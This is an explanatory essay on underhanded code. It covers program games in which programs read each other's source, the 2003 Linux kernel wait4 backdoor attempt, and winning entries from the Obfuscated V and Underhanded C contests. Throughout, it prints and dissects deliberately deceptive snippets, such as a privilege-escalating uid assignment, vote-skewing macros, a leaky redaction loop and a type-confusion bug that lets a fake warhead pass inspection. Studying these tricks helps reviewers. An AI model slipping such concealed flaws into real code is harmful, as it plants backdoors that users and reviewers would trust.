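# Underhanded code contests and smart contract honeypots as precedents for disguised program behavior

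## Reading a program before trusting it

Underhanded code is source code that looks clear and innocent but is designed to misbehave. Programmers have written it for contests, where judges reward the trick that best survives inspection, and occasionally for real attacks. It also matters in a branch of game theory where programs read each other's source code before choosing whether to cooperate. A player in such a game could submit a program with a concealed defection branch, which is code that makes the program defect under some condition and that a reader will probably overlook.

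A short Python program can serve as an example. Its input, `theirs`, is the text of the opponent's program, and its output is C (cooperate) or D (defect).

```python
# Cooperate with any opponent that is a working program.
def play(theirs):
    if theirs.find("def "):    # it defines a function
        return "C"
    return "D"                 # empty or broken entry
```

Python's `find` returns the position of the first match, counting from 0, or −1 if there is no match. `if` treats 0 as false and every other number as true, so the program defects only when the opponent's text begins with the four characters `def ` (including the space). Most readers will think the `if` line checks whether the text contains a function definition. The program cooperates with an opponent that has a comment or an import line at the top. It also cooperates with an empty file, though the last comment leads a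 reader to expect defection.

A trigger is the condition under which disguised code misbehaves. Here the trigger is a property of the opponent's text, but elsewhere it may be a date, a particular caller or a block number on a blockchain. A reader who runs the program against a copy of itself instead of analyzing it will see both cooperate, because the copy opens with a comment. The trick also gives its author plausible deniability. If someone notices it, it could pass for an honest error, because beginners in Python make the same mistake with `find`.

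*Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (Wheeler, 2020) surveyed the public examples and deliberately excluded obfuscated code, which is openly hard to read. Wheeler mentions a converter that rewrites any JavaScript program using only six punctuation marks. A reviewer can reject the result as unreadable without working out what it does, but underhanded code gives the reviewer no such reason. Underhanded code is harder to distinguish from an honest bug, because the two can be identical character for character and differ only in what the author intended. Wheeler found that many samples reused mistakes that programmers already make by accident, such as writing past the end of an array or typing `=` where C requires `==`. The author's intention matters to a project deciding whether to ban a contributor, but it makes no difference to someone who is about to lose money to the program.

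### Programs as players

In the Prisoner's Dilemma two players each choose to cooperate or defect, and neither knows the other's choice. A common version has these payoffs, with the row player's listed first:

| | Other cooperates | Other defects |
|---|---|---|
| **Cooperate** | 3, 3 | 0, 5 |
| **Defect** | 5, 0 | 1, 1 |

Game theorists label the four numbers T = 5 (temptation), R = 3 (reward), P = 1 (punishment) and S = 0 (the sucker's payoff). Defecting always scores higher than cooperating: 5 instead of 3 if the other player cooperates, and 1 instead of 0 if the other player defects. Two players who reason this way therefore get 1 each, when they could have had 3 each by cooperating. The `find` program scores 5 against a plain cooperator whose code begins with `def`, and the cooperator scores 0.

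In a program game, players submit programs instead of choosing moves. Each program receives the other's text and outputs a move. Tennenholtz (2004), in *Program Equilibrium*, defined a program equilibrium as a set of programs in which no player could earn more by replacing only their own. For the Prisoner's Dilemma, Tennenholtz proposed a one-line program that cooperates if the other program is identical to it and defects otherwise. If both players submit it, they get 3 each. If one submits anything else, the texts no longer match, so the other player's program defects and the player who switched gets at most 1. This makes cooperation stable in a single round, which it cannot be in the ordinary game. Barasz, Christiano and colleagues (2014), in *Robust Cooperation in the Prisoner's Dilemma*, credit Howard and McAfee with the same idea in earlier papers and call the program CliqueBot.

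A stable program equilibrium can be unfair. Tennenholtz also proved that a program equilibrium can give players any payoffs their strategies can produce, provided each player gets at least as much as the others could limit them to. In the Prisoner's Dilemma, that minimum is 1. In Filan's (2026) interview *49 - Caspar Oesterheld on Program Equilibrium*, Oesterheld, who researches these games, gives the example of a pact in which one program always cooperates and the other cooperates 60% of the time. With the payoffs above, the player whose program always cooperates averages 1.8 and the other averages 3.8, but the first player still has no reason to leave the pact.

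### Matching, proving and simulating

CliqueBot cooperates only when its opponent's source code matches its own exactly. It checks the code without interpreting it, so disguise does not work. A concealed branch would add characters and break the match, and CliqueBot would defect. By Barasz and colleagues' definition, CliqueBot is unexploitable, meaning that no opponent can defect against it while it cooperates. Somebody still has to read the shared text before the players adopt it. In Tennenholtz's general construction, each copy can act differently depending on which player it represents, so a trick in the shared text could favor one side.

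The drawback is that CliqueBot refuses to cooperate with almost every other program. An irrelevant change to a comment is enough to make two near-copies defect against each other, as Critch (2016) notes in *Parametric Bounded Löb's Theorem and Robust Cooperation of Bounded Agents*. An extra space has the same effect, and so does rewriting the rule in the equivalent form "if the programs differ, defect, else cooperate". Levine (2026), in *Math for AI safety*, calls CliqueBot a "poor citizen" for this reason. Its programmer could add a list of approved texts, but then whoever draws up the list has to decide which programs to trust.

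A program can instead try to prove what its opponent will do. *Cooperative and uncooperative institution designs* (Critch, Dennis and Russell, 2022) introduces DupocBot, short for "defect unless proof of cooperation". DupocBot checks each string of up to k characters to see whether it is a valid formal proof that the opponent will cooperate with DupocBot. If it finds such a proof, it cooperates; otherwise it defects.

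Comments and reassuring variable names do not count as evidence in a formal proof. Suppose DupocBot's own text begins with `def` and it meets the `find` program, which will therefore defect. A sound proof system cannot prove a false statement, so DupocBot finds no proof that the program will cooperate. It defects too, without having to detect the hidden branch or check for one, and both get 1. If DupocBot's text had begun with a comment, the trigger would not have fired, a proof of cooperation would exist, and with a large enough budget both would get 3.

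For large k, two DupocBots also cooperate with each other. This is less obvious, since each seems to wait for a proof about the other's search. When Critch and colleagues asked about 100 computer science graduate students and faculty, around 95% guessed that the search would fail. Let φ be the statement that both copies cooperate. If a short enough proof of φ exists, both copies find it and cooperate, which makes φ true, and the proof system can verify this implication. By Löb's theorem, a system able to prove "if φ is provable, then φ" can also prove φ. Critch proved a version for proofs of limited length, which supplies the proof both copies are searching for. How large k must be is still open, and Levine lists finding an explicit threshold among the problems for mathematicians to solve.

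DupocBot's caution also makes it miss chances to cooperate. It defects against an opponent made of "spaghetti code", too tangled for its search to analyze within its budget, even if that opponent would have cooperated. It would probably do the same against a large neural network. CupodBot is DupocBot's mirror image, a program that cooperates unless it finds a proof of defection. In *Formalization, Transparency, and Collusion in Open-Source Game Theory*, Duclaux, Formenti and colleagues (2026) proved that when the two meet with equal budgets, CupodBot cooperates and DupocBot defects, whatever the budget.

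CupodBot cooperates with another program unless it can prove, within a set number of characters, that the program will defect. This rule helps anyone who writes disguised code. With a limit of ten characters, CupodBot cooperates even with a program that always defects, because no proof of the defection is that short. With a limit of a billion, Critch and colleagues estimate, it would find a proof. Much human code review follows a similar rule, accepting a patch when nobody has found anything wrong with it.

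A program can also run its opponent and copy what it does, which looks simpler than proof. But if both players do this, each run starts another and the process never ends. In *Robust program equilibrium*, Oesterheld (2018) proposed a program that cooperates without looking with some small probability ε, and otherwise simulates the opponent playing against it and copies the result. When two such programs meet, the simulations stop once one of them cooperates without looking, which takes 20 runs on average if ε is 0.05. The drawback is that a program that always defects gets a payoff of 5 instead of 1 in one game out of 20. Cooper, Oesterheld and Conitzer (2024), in *Characterising Simulation-Based Program Equilibria*, consider simulation more practical than proof because it works on programs that nobody can prove much about.

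Simulation catches the `find` trick because the simulated opponent receives the same text as the real one. Simulation fails against a trigger that is off during the simulation and on in the game. Duclaux and colleagues note that testing in general has this weakness, because a player who sees a program's behavior only on certain test inputs learns nothing about its behavior on others. At least one contestant has tried to exploit this. *Prisoner’s dilemma tournament results* records a contest among 21 programs that could read each other's source, in which Quinn's entry paused for nine seconds before it defected. The entry also contained a condition meant to detect opponents that had removed the pause before running it, though no opponent had.

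Many contestants read far less carefully than DupocBot. According to one commenter, an entry in the same contest cooperated with a program that always defected, because that program's code contained the word "quine" (a program that prints its own text). Filan recalls a later tournament in which many entrants looked for a string that by itself meant "I will cooperate with you", and thinks such checks were better than nothing for programs with little time to compute. But they are very easy to fool, since anyone can paste in the string and defect anyway.

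### When the text is not what runs

All of these methods rely on the inspected text being the program that will run. With smart contracts, the two can differ. A smart contract is a program that a blockchain stores and runs, and it can hold and pay out money. On Ethereum, the best-known platform for smart contracts, developers usually write them in a language called Solidity. A compiler turns this source into bytecode, the instructions that Ethereum's machines execute, and the chain stores only the bytecode. Developers choose whether to publish the source, so a careful reader recompiles the published version and checks that it produces the stored bytecode. Even then, the reader may still misjudge what the source does. Honeypot contracts depend on this mistake, since each shows an apparent flaw as bait and keeps the money of anyone who tries to exploit it. Cooper and colleagues name smart contracts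 among the interactions that program games could model. Smart contracts fit closely because their code is open to inspection, they act without further consent from anyone, and misreading them costs money.

### What a reader can and cannot decide

Rice's theorem, from 1951, shows that no procedure can correctly answer a question about behavior for every program, unless the answer is the same for all programs. This rules out a tool that can always tell whether a program will ever defect. If such a tool existed, we could take any computation and write a program that carries it out and then defects. That program would defect only if the computation finished, so the tool could be used to determine whether any computation finishes. Alan Turing had already shown that no general method can do this.

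Despite the theorem, a reader can still prove things about particular programs and refuse to trust those it cannot verify, as DupocBot does. The players can also agree on a simpler language; Tennenholtz allowed only programs without loops, which always halt. Cooper and colleagues wanted to know whether an opponent's move depends on its private random numbers. The theorem rules out a general procedure for this, so their program checks whether the opponent accesses those numbers at all. An opponent that reads a random number and then ignores it fails the check, even though its move doesn't depend on the number.

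A reader can be judged by its detection rate, the share of disguised programs it flags, and its false alarm rate, the share of honest programs it wrongly flags. CliqueBot flags every program that is not its exact copy, including nearly every honest one. Readers that judge without proof, such as the language models that *Evaluating LLMs in Open-Source Games* (2025) tests on more than 230 human-written strategies, can both miss disguised programs and flag honest ones.

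The payoffs of the Prisoner's Dilemma determine how accurate such a reader must be. Let d be the chance that the reader flags a disguised program and f the chance that it flags an honest one. Suppose the reader defects against every program it flags and cooperates with the rest, and that honest programs predict a defection and defect too. An honest program then scores 3 if it passes and 1 if it is flagged, for an average of 3 − 2f. A disguised program scores 5 if it passes and 1 if it is flagged, for an average of 5 − 4d. Disguise therefore gives no advantage once d is at least (1 + f)/2. A reader that never flags honest programs must catch at least half of the disguised ones, and a reader that flags a fifth of honest programs must catch at least 60%.

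That threshold applies to the best disguise an author can devise, which may be much harder to catch than the average example in a test set. It also assumes that the reader's verdict on the same text varies between readings. If the reader is a fixed, deterministic program, each text always passes or always fails, and an author who can study the reader beforehand needs to find only one that passes.

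## 2003 and 2004: the Linux kernel attempt and the vote-counting contest

In November 2003 someone added two lines to a public copy of the source code of the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system. The lines looked like a routine error check, but they would have let an ordinary user take complete control of any machine running a kernel built from that copy.

### What the two lines did

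The lines went into `wait4`, a function that programs call to wait for another program to finish. The last line below was already there.

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
retval = -ECHILD;
```

`options` holds settings chosen by the calling program, `current->uid` is the ID of the user running that program, and `retval` is the result `wait4` will return. User ID 0 belongs to root, the administrator account, which can do anything on the machine. Someone skimming the new lines will take them to mean "if the caller has set this odd pair of options and is root, return an error".

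But in C, `==` compares two values and a single `=` stores one. Gervase Markham explained the consequences in a 2003 reader comment on LWN's *An attempt to backdoor the kernel*. Suppose a user's program calls `wait4` with exactly those two options:

1. The comparison on the left of `&&` is true, so C goes on to evaluate the right-hand side. With any other options it would stop here.
2. The right-hand side stores 0 in `current->uid`. The program is now running as root.
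3. In C an assignment also has a value, which is the value it stored. That value is 0, which C treats as false, so the whole condition is false and C skips the error line.
4. `wait4` carries on as usual, and the program keeps root's powers.

Anyone who could already run a program on the machine could have done this, but an outsider with no account could not. The two options that triggered it specify conflicting kinds of waiting, so legitimate programs have no reason to combine them, and ordinary use would almost never have triggered it. Larry McVoy, whose company hosted the code, said in Poulsen's *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (2003) that the attacker had to find options that `wait4` would accept but that programs don't normally use together.

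The standard Linux compiler, gcc, would not have flagged the change. It can warn about a single `=` in a condition, but not if the assignment has its own parentheses, as it does here. Markham thought the attacker must have known this. The parentheses are weak evidence of that, though, because the line would not compile without them.

### How the change came to light

At the time, Linux developers kept the master copy of the kernel in a system called BitKeeper, where every change went through an approval process. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so McVoy's company, BitMover, also published a copy through an older system called CVS. An automatic process generated the CVS copy, and nobody was supposed to edit it by hand. The intruder apparently broke into the server and edited that copy directly.

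Felten writes in *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) that McVoy noticed a change with no pointer to a record of its approval. Corbet, who reported the attempt for the Linux news site LWN, likewise said that the changes lacked the usual links to BitKeeper and "thus stood out immediately" (quoted in InfoQ's *A Look Back at the Linux Kernel Backdoor*, 2013).

The kernel mailing list thread that starts with McVoy (2003), *BK2CVS problem*, describes an earlier step. Every night a script compared checksums, which are short fingerprints of a file's contents, for the public CVS copy and BitMover's internal one, and sent an email if they differed. On 5 November one file did not match. McVoy looked at its history and found three entries from the day before that lacked the usual pointer. They carried the name of David Miller, a well-known kernel developer, who denied making them.

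A mismatch in the records exposed the change before people worked out what it did. In his first message, McVoy called the incident "not a big deal" and did not include the changed lines. Another developer asked to see them out of curiosity. Twenty-five minutes after McVoy posted them, Chad Kitching replied that they looked like an attempt to plant a backdoor, a hidden way of getting access. McVoy acknowledged that he had missed this.

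Those 25 minutes are weak evidence of how well code review would have worked, because the developers were looking at two isolated lines and already knew that someone had inserted them without permission. A reviewer who came across the same lines in the middle of a long patch would have neither advantage.

Like CliqueBot's exact matching, the nightly comparison could detect any alteration without interpreting the code. But it needed a trusted original, and it would have missed the two lines if the attacker had got them into the master copy by the normal route. In the same thread, Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, raised the possibility that an attacker could do this by forging an email from a trusted colleague and burying a small change among plausible ones.

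People disagreed about how close the change came to an official release. Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux development, said it had no way to reach one. Changes reached a release either through BitKeeper, whose users would not have touched the CVS copy, or by email to Torvalds, who would read through any patch to a core file. Poulsen suggested that a developer could have started from the altered CVS file and emailed in work that included the two lines. One LWN commenter objected that the CVS command for listing a developer's changes leaves out other people's edits, so a developer who used it correctly would not have sent those lines.

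Ryan Russell, a security consultant, told Poulsen that the backdoor was "indistinguishable from an accidental bug". That is fair for the missing `=`, a very common slip. The rest of the code is harder to explain as a mistake, because it makes little sense even with `==` in place. InfoQ points out that the user ID is irrelevant to `wait4`. A commenter on Felten's post asks why anyone would forbid a harmless pair of options, and only for root. Kitching noticed that the next line overwrites `retval`, so the error code would have been lost anyway. A reviewer who asked what the check was for could have rejected it without spotting the missing character.

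The break-in itself ruled out an innocent explanation for most observers. Nobody has publicly identified the intruder.

### A contest for dishonest vote counters

Within a week, Douglas Jones, a computer scientist at the University of Iowa, applied the case to voting machines. Examiners were checking the machines' source code behind closed doors. In *How a backdoor in the Linux kernel was thwarted, from RISKS*, Jones (2003) called the kernel attempt a good example of what these examiners had to catch. The coding rules for voting systems already banned assignments inside conditions, but Jones expected a capable attacker to obey them and hide the trick elsewhere.

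A year later, Daniel Horn invited programmers to write such tricks. In *Obfuscated Vote Counting Contest*, Horn (2004) said he was inspired by an existing contest for unreadable C programs and by the electronic voting scandals of the time. Despite its name, the Obfuscated V Contest was for underhanded code, since Horn wanted programs that appeared correct. Wheeler found no earlier underhanded code contest, and Horn's inspired the better-known Underhanded C Contest.

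The rules, on Horn's page *The Obfuscated V contest*, required a program to read a string of characters and count each K as a vote for Kerry, each B for Bush and each N for Nader, the candidates in that year's US presidential election. It had to skip blanks and count everything else as "Other". Horn supplied a correct program as a starting point. Entrants had to make the count favor one candidate, with bonus points if the total number of votes was still correct. Comparing the number of votes with the number of voters will expose a program that invents votes, but not one that moves votes between candidates.

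Horn's rules set out two categories. Programs in the first would be run on 1 November and had to print a correct tally, then cheat on 2 November, election day. Programs in the second could cheat on any day. On election day, judges would read the entries and choose the one in each category that looked most correct. If it miscounted when they ran it, it would win; otherwise they would move on to the next most convincing entry.

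Horn later published scores out of 10 for 41 entries, nine of which had a date trigger. The scores combined creativity, believability and the accuracy of the totals. Accuracy counted because an error of only a few percent is harder to notice.

### Why the date matters

Testers usually check a vote counter by giving it ballots with a known result. A program that cheats every day will fail some of these tests on any date, and Wheeler concludes that good tests could expose every entry of this kind. The tests do need enough ballots. Michal Zalewski's winning entry diverted about one vote in ten, so a test with three ballots could easily miss it, but a test with a hundred ballots for other candidates would almost certainly catch it.

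Testing with more ballots does not expose a date trigger. A program that miscounts only on election day will count every set of ballots correctly on 1 November, and testers rarely think of the date as an input. Setting the computer's clock forward to election day would catch a simple trigger, but testers have to guess what the trigger is, and an author can add further conditions. Jasvir Nagra's entry apparently needed both the right date and a two-digit hour, so a test with the clock set to nine o'clock on election morning would have found nothing wrong.

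Testers can also check whether their tests have run every line of the program, but this exposes cheating only if the code for it is on separate lines. Wheeler, who also entered the contest, submitted a program with a separate block of code for election day. He said that tests covering every line would "trivially" find the problem.

Paul Parkanzky's winning entry in the date category avoided that weakness. The program writes text into a fixed space in memory that is too small when the text includes the word "second", as in the second of November. "First" and "third" are one letter shorter and fit. On election day the text spills into neighboring memory, which gives votes to Bush. The instruction that does the damage can also run harmlessly the day before, so a record of which lines had run would not single it out. The trick is also plausibly deniable, because C programmers often reserve too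 little space by accident.

### Two entries in code

Scott Craver's entry combined a date trigger with a look-alike character. The line that adds to Bush's count reads:

```c
total = total+l;
```

The last character before the semicolon is a variable named `l`, a lowercase L that most readers will see as the digit 1. It has to equal 1 on ordinary days for the count to be right, but on election day the program sets it to 104, so each vote for Bush counts as 104 votes. The entry scored 5.0. Wheeler considers variables named `l` and `o` suspicious in themselves, and doubts that the program would work on typical systems. The program also inflates the vote total, which a comparison with the number of voters would reveal.

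David Mazieres reused a name instead, in an entry that cheats every day. It relies on a macro, a named piece of text that the compiler pastes into the program wherever the name appears. These are the two important lines:

```c
ptrdiff_t c = val;    /* inside the macro tabulate(val) */

tabulate (c);         /* where the program uses the macro */
```

The second line appears to hand the value of `c` to the macro, which refers to it as `val`. But the compiler only substitutes text, so it replaces `val` with `c` and produces this:

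```c
ptrdiff_t c = c;
```

This creates a new variable, also called `c`, and sets it to its own value. The new variable has no value yet, so it gets whatever happens to be in that part of memory. Inside the macro, the new `c` hides the original. Each line looks fine on its own, and a reader has to consider them together to see the problem.

Mazieres scored 5.3. Zalewski used the same kind of name collision and scored 7.3, the highest in the contest. About one time in ten, Zalewski's macro creates its own variable `t`, which hides the one that points to the voter's chosen candidate. The vote then goes to the first candidate on the list, but the total stays correct.

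Two entrants used the trick from the kernel attempt, `=` in place of `==`, and both scored 3.3, close to the lowest score of 3.0. These low scores do not show that reviewers would usually catch the trick, because Horn's judges were looking for tricks and gave credit for originality. McVoy missed it even though he already suspected a break-in.

The judges also knew that every program was supposed to cheat. Their scores rank the disguises but don't give a detection rate or a false alarm rate, because there were no honest programs among the entries.

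Even readers who know that a program cheats can misunderstand how. Wheeler re-examined the entries for a later study of automatic tools and found that four of Horn's one-sentence explanations were wrong, misleading or about an attack missing from the published file. Horn had blamed a swap between the letter O and the digit 0 for the cheating in Ryan Cumings's entry. The entry did contain that swap, but the main problem was that it chose where to record each vote with the expression `vote % 2`, the remainder after dividing by 2. The remainder can only be 0 or 1, so every vote went to one of the first two rows of the table.

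## 2005 to 2015: the Underhanded C Contest

Horn's vote-counting contest impressed Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, because it showed that even a program that only counts characters could miscount on one chosen day. In 2005 Craver started the Underhanded C Contest, which gave entrants an ordinary task for a C program and a harmful behavior to hide in it. According to the contest's *FAQ*, Craver wanted to identify such tricks and find out what makes them possible. He denied that the contest was an argument against open-source software and said that it showed the need for "more code review, not less".

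The contest ran every year from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015. Its *Hall of Fame* page lists the winners.

| Year | The program's job | What it also had to do | Winner |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2005 | Process an image | Hide a different fingerprint in every output | Pihlaja and V-Khuong; Shin (joint) |
| 2006 | Count the words in a text | Run very slowly on one operating system | Brogan |
| 2007 | Encrypt a file | Encrypt a small fraction of files weakly | Colbus |
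| 2008 | Block out parts of an image | Leave the hidden parts recoverable | Meacham |
| 2009 | Look up airline luggage records | Misroute a bag when a clerk types a certain comment | Blackburn |
| 2013 | Measure how closely two users of a social network are connected | Give one account access it should not have | Olson |
| 2014 | Copy posts that match a secret surveillance request | Let the user find out | Pease |
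| 2015 | Compare a scan of a warhead with a reference scan | Accept a fake | Åkesson |

### What earned points

The scoring rules changed little over the years. Craver (2014) described them in the most detail in *The 7th Underhanded C Contest is now Open*. Most of the rules correspond to a mistake people make when reading code.

Short, readable programs earned more points. *The 2005 challenge*, the contest's page for its first year, explains that a long file looks less innocent because its author can hide more in it. The 2007 rules said that a source file over 200 lines was unlikely to win, according to an extract in Shostack + Friends Blog's *Weak Crypto Contest* (2007). The winning programs of 2008, 2013 and 2015 had 55, 54 and 66 lines. Wheeler described underhanded code on a security mailing list as "easy to understand WRONGLY", and someone who has read every line of such a short program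 will probably feel sure they understand it.

An entry also scored higher if it still looked innocent under syntax coloring. Most programmers read code in an editor that shows comments, strings and keywords in different colors. This exposes some disguises, such as a working instruction that looks like part of a comment. But the colors only show the type of each piece of text. Lena Olson's 2014 entry used 5,000,000 microseconds for half a second instead of 500,000, and an editor gives both numbers the same color.

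Judges also rewarded plausible deniability, which lets the author keep the job and try again after a reader finds and fixes the bug. The 2009 task required an excuse for both the programmer and the airline clerk who types the trigger. Mason Malone's entry let the clerk change the luggage database by typing database commands into the comment field. Programmers often leave that security hole by accident, but *The 2009 challenge* points out that the clerk's comment would look like an attack.

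In the contest, a trick that made readers mistake an `l` for a 1 counted for as much as one that used memory or number formats. Bad code gets through whether a reader overlooks a character or sees it but doesn't know what C does with it.

The rules also covered how the bug was triggered. In 2013, a bug was rare enough to qualify if it fired by chance no more than 1% of the time. In 2015, entries scored higher if the cheater could easily set up the triggering conditions but they rarely arose by accident. Users would soon notice a bug that fired often, even if the source code looked innocent.

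Finally, the contest gave extra points for humor and spite, such as hiding a bug inside an error-checking routine. This was partly a joke, but reviewers look for missing checks, and seeing one in place probably reassures them.

### 2008: blocked-out pixels that leak

The 2008 task was to write a program that blocks out rectangles in an image, as an office might do before releasing a scanned document. Many of the more than 100 entrants either scrambled the pixels in a way that an attacker could reverse or appended the original data to the end of the file, where image viewers ignore it. *This year's challenge*, the contest's page for 2008, points out that somebody might notice the extra data, and that scrambling pixels looks odd when the program could simply erase them, as John Meacham's entry did.

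Meacham's program works on a text version of the PPM image format. Each pixel is three numbers, for red, green and blue, in ordinary digits. If the maximum is 255, a white pixel is `255 255 255` and a black one is `0 0 0`. Simplified and with clearer names, the central part of the program works like this:

```c
for (p = text; *p; p++) {
    if (!isdigit(*p)) {        // a space or line break
        in_number = 0;
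        putchar(*p);
        continue;
    }
    if (!in_number) {          // first digit of the next number
        in_number = 1;
        next_position();
    }
    if (inside_rectangle())
        putchar('0');
    else
        putchar(*p);
}
```

The loop goes through the text one character at a time. `next_position` and `inside_rectangle` stand for a few lines of arithmetic that track the position in the image and check whether it is inside the rectangle. The program prints a 0 in place of each digit inside the rectangle and copies everything else unchanged, including the spaces between numbers.

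Suppose the rectangle covers a white pixel, a dark gray one and a black one:

```
before:   255 255 255    64 64 64    0 0 0
after:    000 000 000    00 00 00    0 0 0
```

An image viewer treats `000`, `00` and `0` as the same number, so it shows three black pixels. But the number of zeros reveals whether each original value was below 10, between 10 and 99, or at least 100. For a scan of pure black text on white paper, this is enough to recover every letter, because the ink becomes `0` and the paper becomes `000`. A color photograph leaks less. If all 256 values are equally common, a little over one of the eight bits in each number survives.

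Meacham's program has no trigger and leaks every time it runs, but ordinary tests miss the leak. A tester who opens the output sees a solid black rectangle, a script that checks each pixel in the rectangle finds a zero, and the file is the same size as before. A tester could detect the leak by redacting two images that differ only inside the rectangle and comparing the resulting files byte by byte, since any difference would reveal something about the redacted pixels.

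No line of the loop is wrong by itself, and `putchar('0')` does replace each digit in the rectangle with a zero. The error is that the program erases digits one by one when it should erase whole numbers. A reader who checks only whether every pixel in the rectangle turns black will find that it does, but the document is secure only if the output no longer depends on what was there before. The mistake is also easy to excuse, since replacing digits saves the programmer from converting text to numbers and back.

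### 2015: a warhead inspection that accepts fakes

The nonprofit Nuclear Threat Initiative sponsored the 2015 contest and helped design the task. In the task's scenario, two countries have agreed to destroy warheads, and inspectors must confirm that each one contains real nuclear material. A gamma-ray scan would show this, but it would also reveal secrets about the weapon's design. The countries therefore agree on a program that compares the scan with a reference and outputs only yes or no. Entrants had to write the comparison so that the inspected country could pass off a fake warhead as real.

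Linus Åkesson won, and published the entry as a puzzle in *Faking Fissile Material* (2016). Its documentation describes a sensible method. Each scan is a list of counts, one for each of a series of energy ranges, or bins. The program works in three steps:

1. It rejects the test object if its total count is too small a fraction of the reference total.
2. It smooths both lists by averaging 16 neighboring bins, takes the difference between each bin and the next, and smooths again, to bring out the peaks.
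3. It computes a standard measure of similarity, which is 1 for two lists of exactly the same shape, and accepts the object if the result reaches a threshold. The documentation recommends 0.6.

The code is in three files. These are the lines that matter, shortened and with new comments:

```c
/* File 1: match.h */
typedef double float_t;    /* number type for the scans */
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length);

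/* File 2: match.c */
#include "match.h"
/* last step, where t and r are the two smoothed scans */
return spectral_contrast(t, r, bins) >= threshold;

/* File 3: spectral_contrast.c */
#include <math.h>          /* for square roots */
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length) {
    /* scale both lists to the same length, then compare them */
}
```

The two files use different definitions of `float_t`, though they look consistent to a reader. `match.h` defines it as a `double` (an 8-byte number), but C compiles each file separately, and `spectral_contrast.c` never includes `match.h`. The compiler would normally report an error for the undefined type, but it finds another `float_t` in the standard header `math.h`, which on most systems is a `float` (a 4-byte number). So `match.c` passes a list of 8-byte numbers to a function that reads 4-byte numbers. The linker, which joins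 the compiled files, doesn't catch the mismatch because it matches C functions by name and doesn't compare their types.

With 1,000 bins, the list takes up 8,000 bytes, but the function reads 1,000 numbers of 4 bytes each. It therefore stops after 4,000 bytes and ignores everything above bin 500.

It also misreads the bins it does reach, because it takes each 8-byte number for two 4-byte ones. Counts are whole numbers of moderate size, which leave the lower half of a `double` empty, so one of the two numbers is always 0. The other is a heavily compressed version of the original:

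| Value in `match.c` | Value in `spectral_contrast.c` |
|---|---|
| 10 | 2.56 |
| 100 | 3.39 |
| 1,000 | 4.48 |

A value 100 times as large as another therefore counts for only 1.75 times as much. According to Åkesson, the result depends on where the peaks are in the left half of the scan and hardly at all on how high they are. The smoothing width of 16 also matters, because dividing by a power of two leaves the lower half of each number empty, while dividing by 15 would usually fill it with digits and disturb the comparison.

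To cheat, the host country leaves a little of the real material in the fake, which puts small peaks in the right places. It also adds another radioactive substance with a strong peak above bin 500. `match.c` computes the total correctly over all the bins, so the added peak gets the fake past the first check, but the comparison ignores that peak. Åkesson simulated 1,000 forgeries that were 10% real material. Many failed, but the host country can choose the best one in advance. Åkesson's example of a good forgery passed at thresholds of up to 0.72, above the recommended 0.6.

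The fault in the source is a missing line, `#include "match.h"`, at the top of the third file. With that line, the compiler would have found two conflicting definitions of `float_t` and reported an error. Programmers often forget such lines, and the compiler usually reports the mistake. Reviewers comment on the lines that are present, and all of those are fine. A reviewer who received only one of the two `.c` files would have nothing to find. Åkesson had relied on this before. In *Obsessbook*, a discussion of a 2013 entry whose bug lay in the interaction between two modules, Åkesson observed that there would be "very little risk of discovery" if each module went to code review separately.

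The trigger is the scan itself. *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) called this a data-triggered attack, in contrast to attacks that rely on the computer's surroundings. Two entrants' programs misbehaved when someone changed the number of available processors, and Stephen Oman's entry needed someone to turn back the clock during the scan. Craver preferred data triggers because they need no further assumptions, though inspection experts had said that tampering with the machine could not be ruled out completely. In a program game, the opponent's source code is the input, so every player can use a data trigger. A trigger based on the clock or the processors is useful only to a player who can predict or influence the machine that runs the game.

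### A comma, a zero and a username

Sam Blackburn's winning program from 2009 removes swear words from clerks' comments. It uses a list in which each word comes before its replacement:

```c
"hell",  "h*ll",
"damn",  "d*mn"
"bitch", "b*tch"
```

The second line has no comma at the end, and C joins neighboring strings, so the replacement for "damn" is the nine-character string `d*mnbitch`. The longer text can overflow the 64 bytes reserved for the comment into the next field in memory, which marks the record for deletion. An angry clerk can make a bag's record disappear by typing "damn" in the comment, and has an excuse for typing it because people do swear in such comments.

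A runner-up in the same year, under the name RHays, hid a bug in a function that compares two strings and copes with missing ones:

```c
return (y != 0 && x == 0 && *y != '\0') || (x != 0 && *x == '0' && x != '\0');
```

In C, `'\0'` marks the end of a string and `'0'` is the digit zero. The second half of the line should check whether `x` is non-empty, but it checks whether `x` begins with the digit. Elsewhere in the program, a second bug makes a loop go one field too far and compare each comment with a missing string. If the function were correct, that loop would drop every record with a comment, and the first test would expose the bug. Because the function checks for the digit instead, the program drops only records whose comment starts with 0, such as "0ffered passenger compensation for his headaches". RHays also included three automatic checks of the function, all of which pass. The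 judges thought the redundant conditions made the code look "just amateurish enough" for the bug to pass as a beginner's mistake.

Alex Olson's 2013 winner decides how close two users of a social network are. Before it does so, it checks that a moderator has not disabled either account. The main file and a second file describe the checking function differently:

```c
void ValidateAccount(const user user, int *isEnabled);    /* main file */
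void ValidateAccount(const user user, long *is_valid)     /* second file */
```

On many systems an `int` takes up 4 bytes and a `long` takes up 8. The main file sets aside 4 bytes for the answer, but the function writes 8, so it also overwrites the next variable, `distance`. For most usernames it fills `distance` with zeros, which is harmless. The function compares the username with the text `!!INVALID!!`, and the result is −1 for a name that comes earlier in alphabetical order, such as `!!!`. Writing −1 as 8 bytes sets both variables to −1. Olson's program records distances as negative numbers, so it treats the two users as direct friends. An account called `!!!` therefore gets full access to every other account, even if it has no friends. In *2013 Winners*, Craver (2014) found the negative distances the only conspicuous feature of the program.

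### Groups of tricks

The programs that won in 2007, 2013 and 2015 all used type confusion, declaring a function differently from its real definition. In 2007 Emmanuel Colbus declared the standard function `time` as taking no input, although it expects an address at which to store the time. The function therefore stored the time at whatever address happened to be next in memory, which overwrote a switch for debugging messages. According to the contest's 2007 page, also titled *This year's challenge*, this turned on a message containing the encryption key about once in 256 runs. The program had closed its normal output channels, so the message went into the encrypted file.

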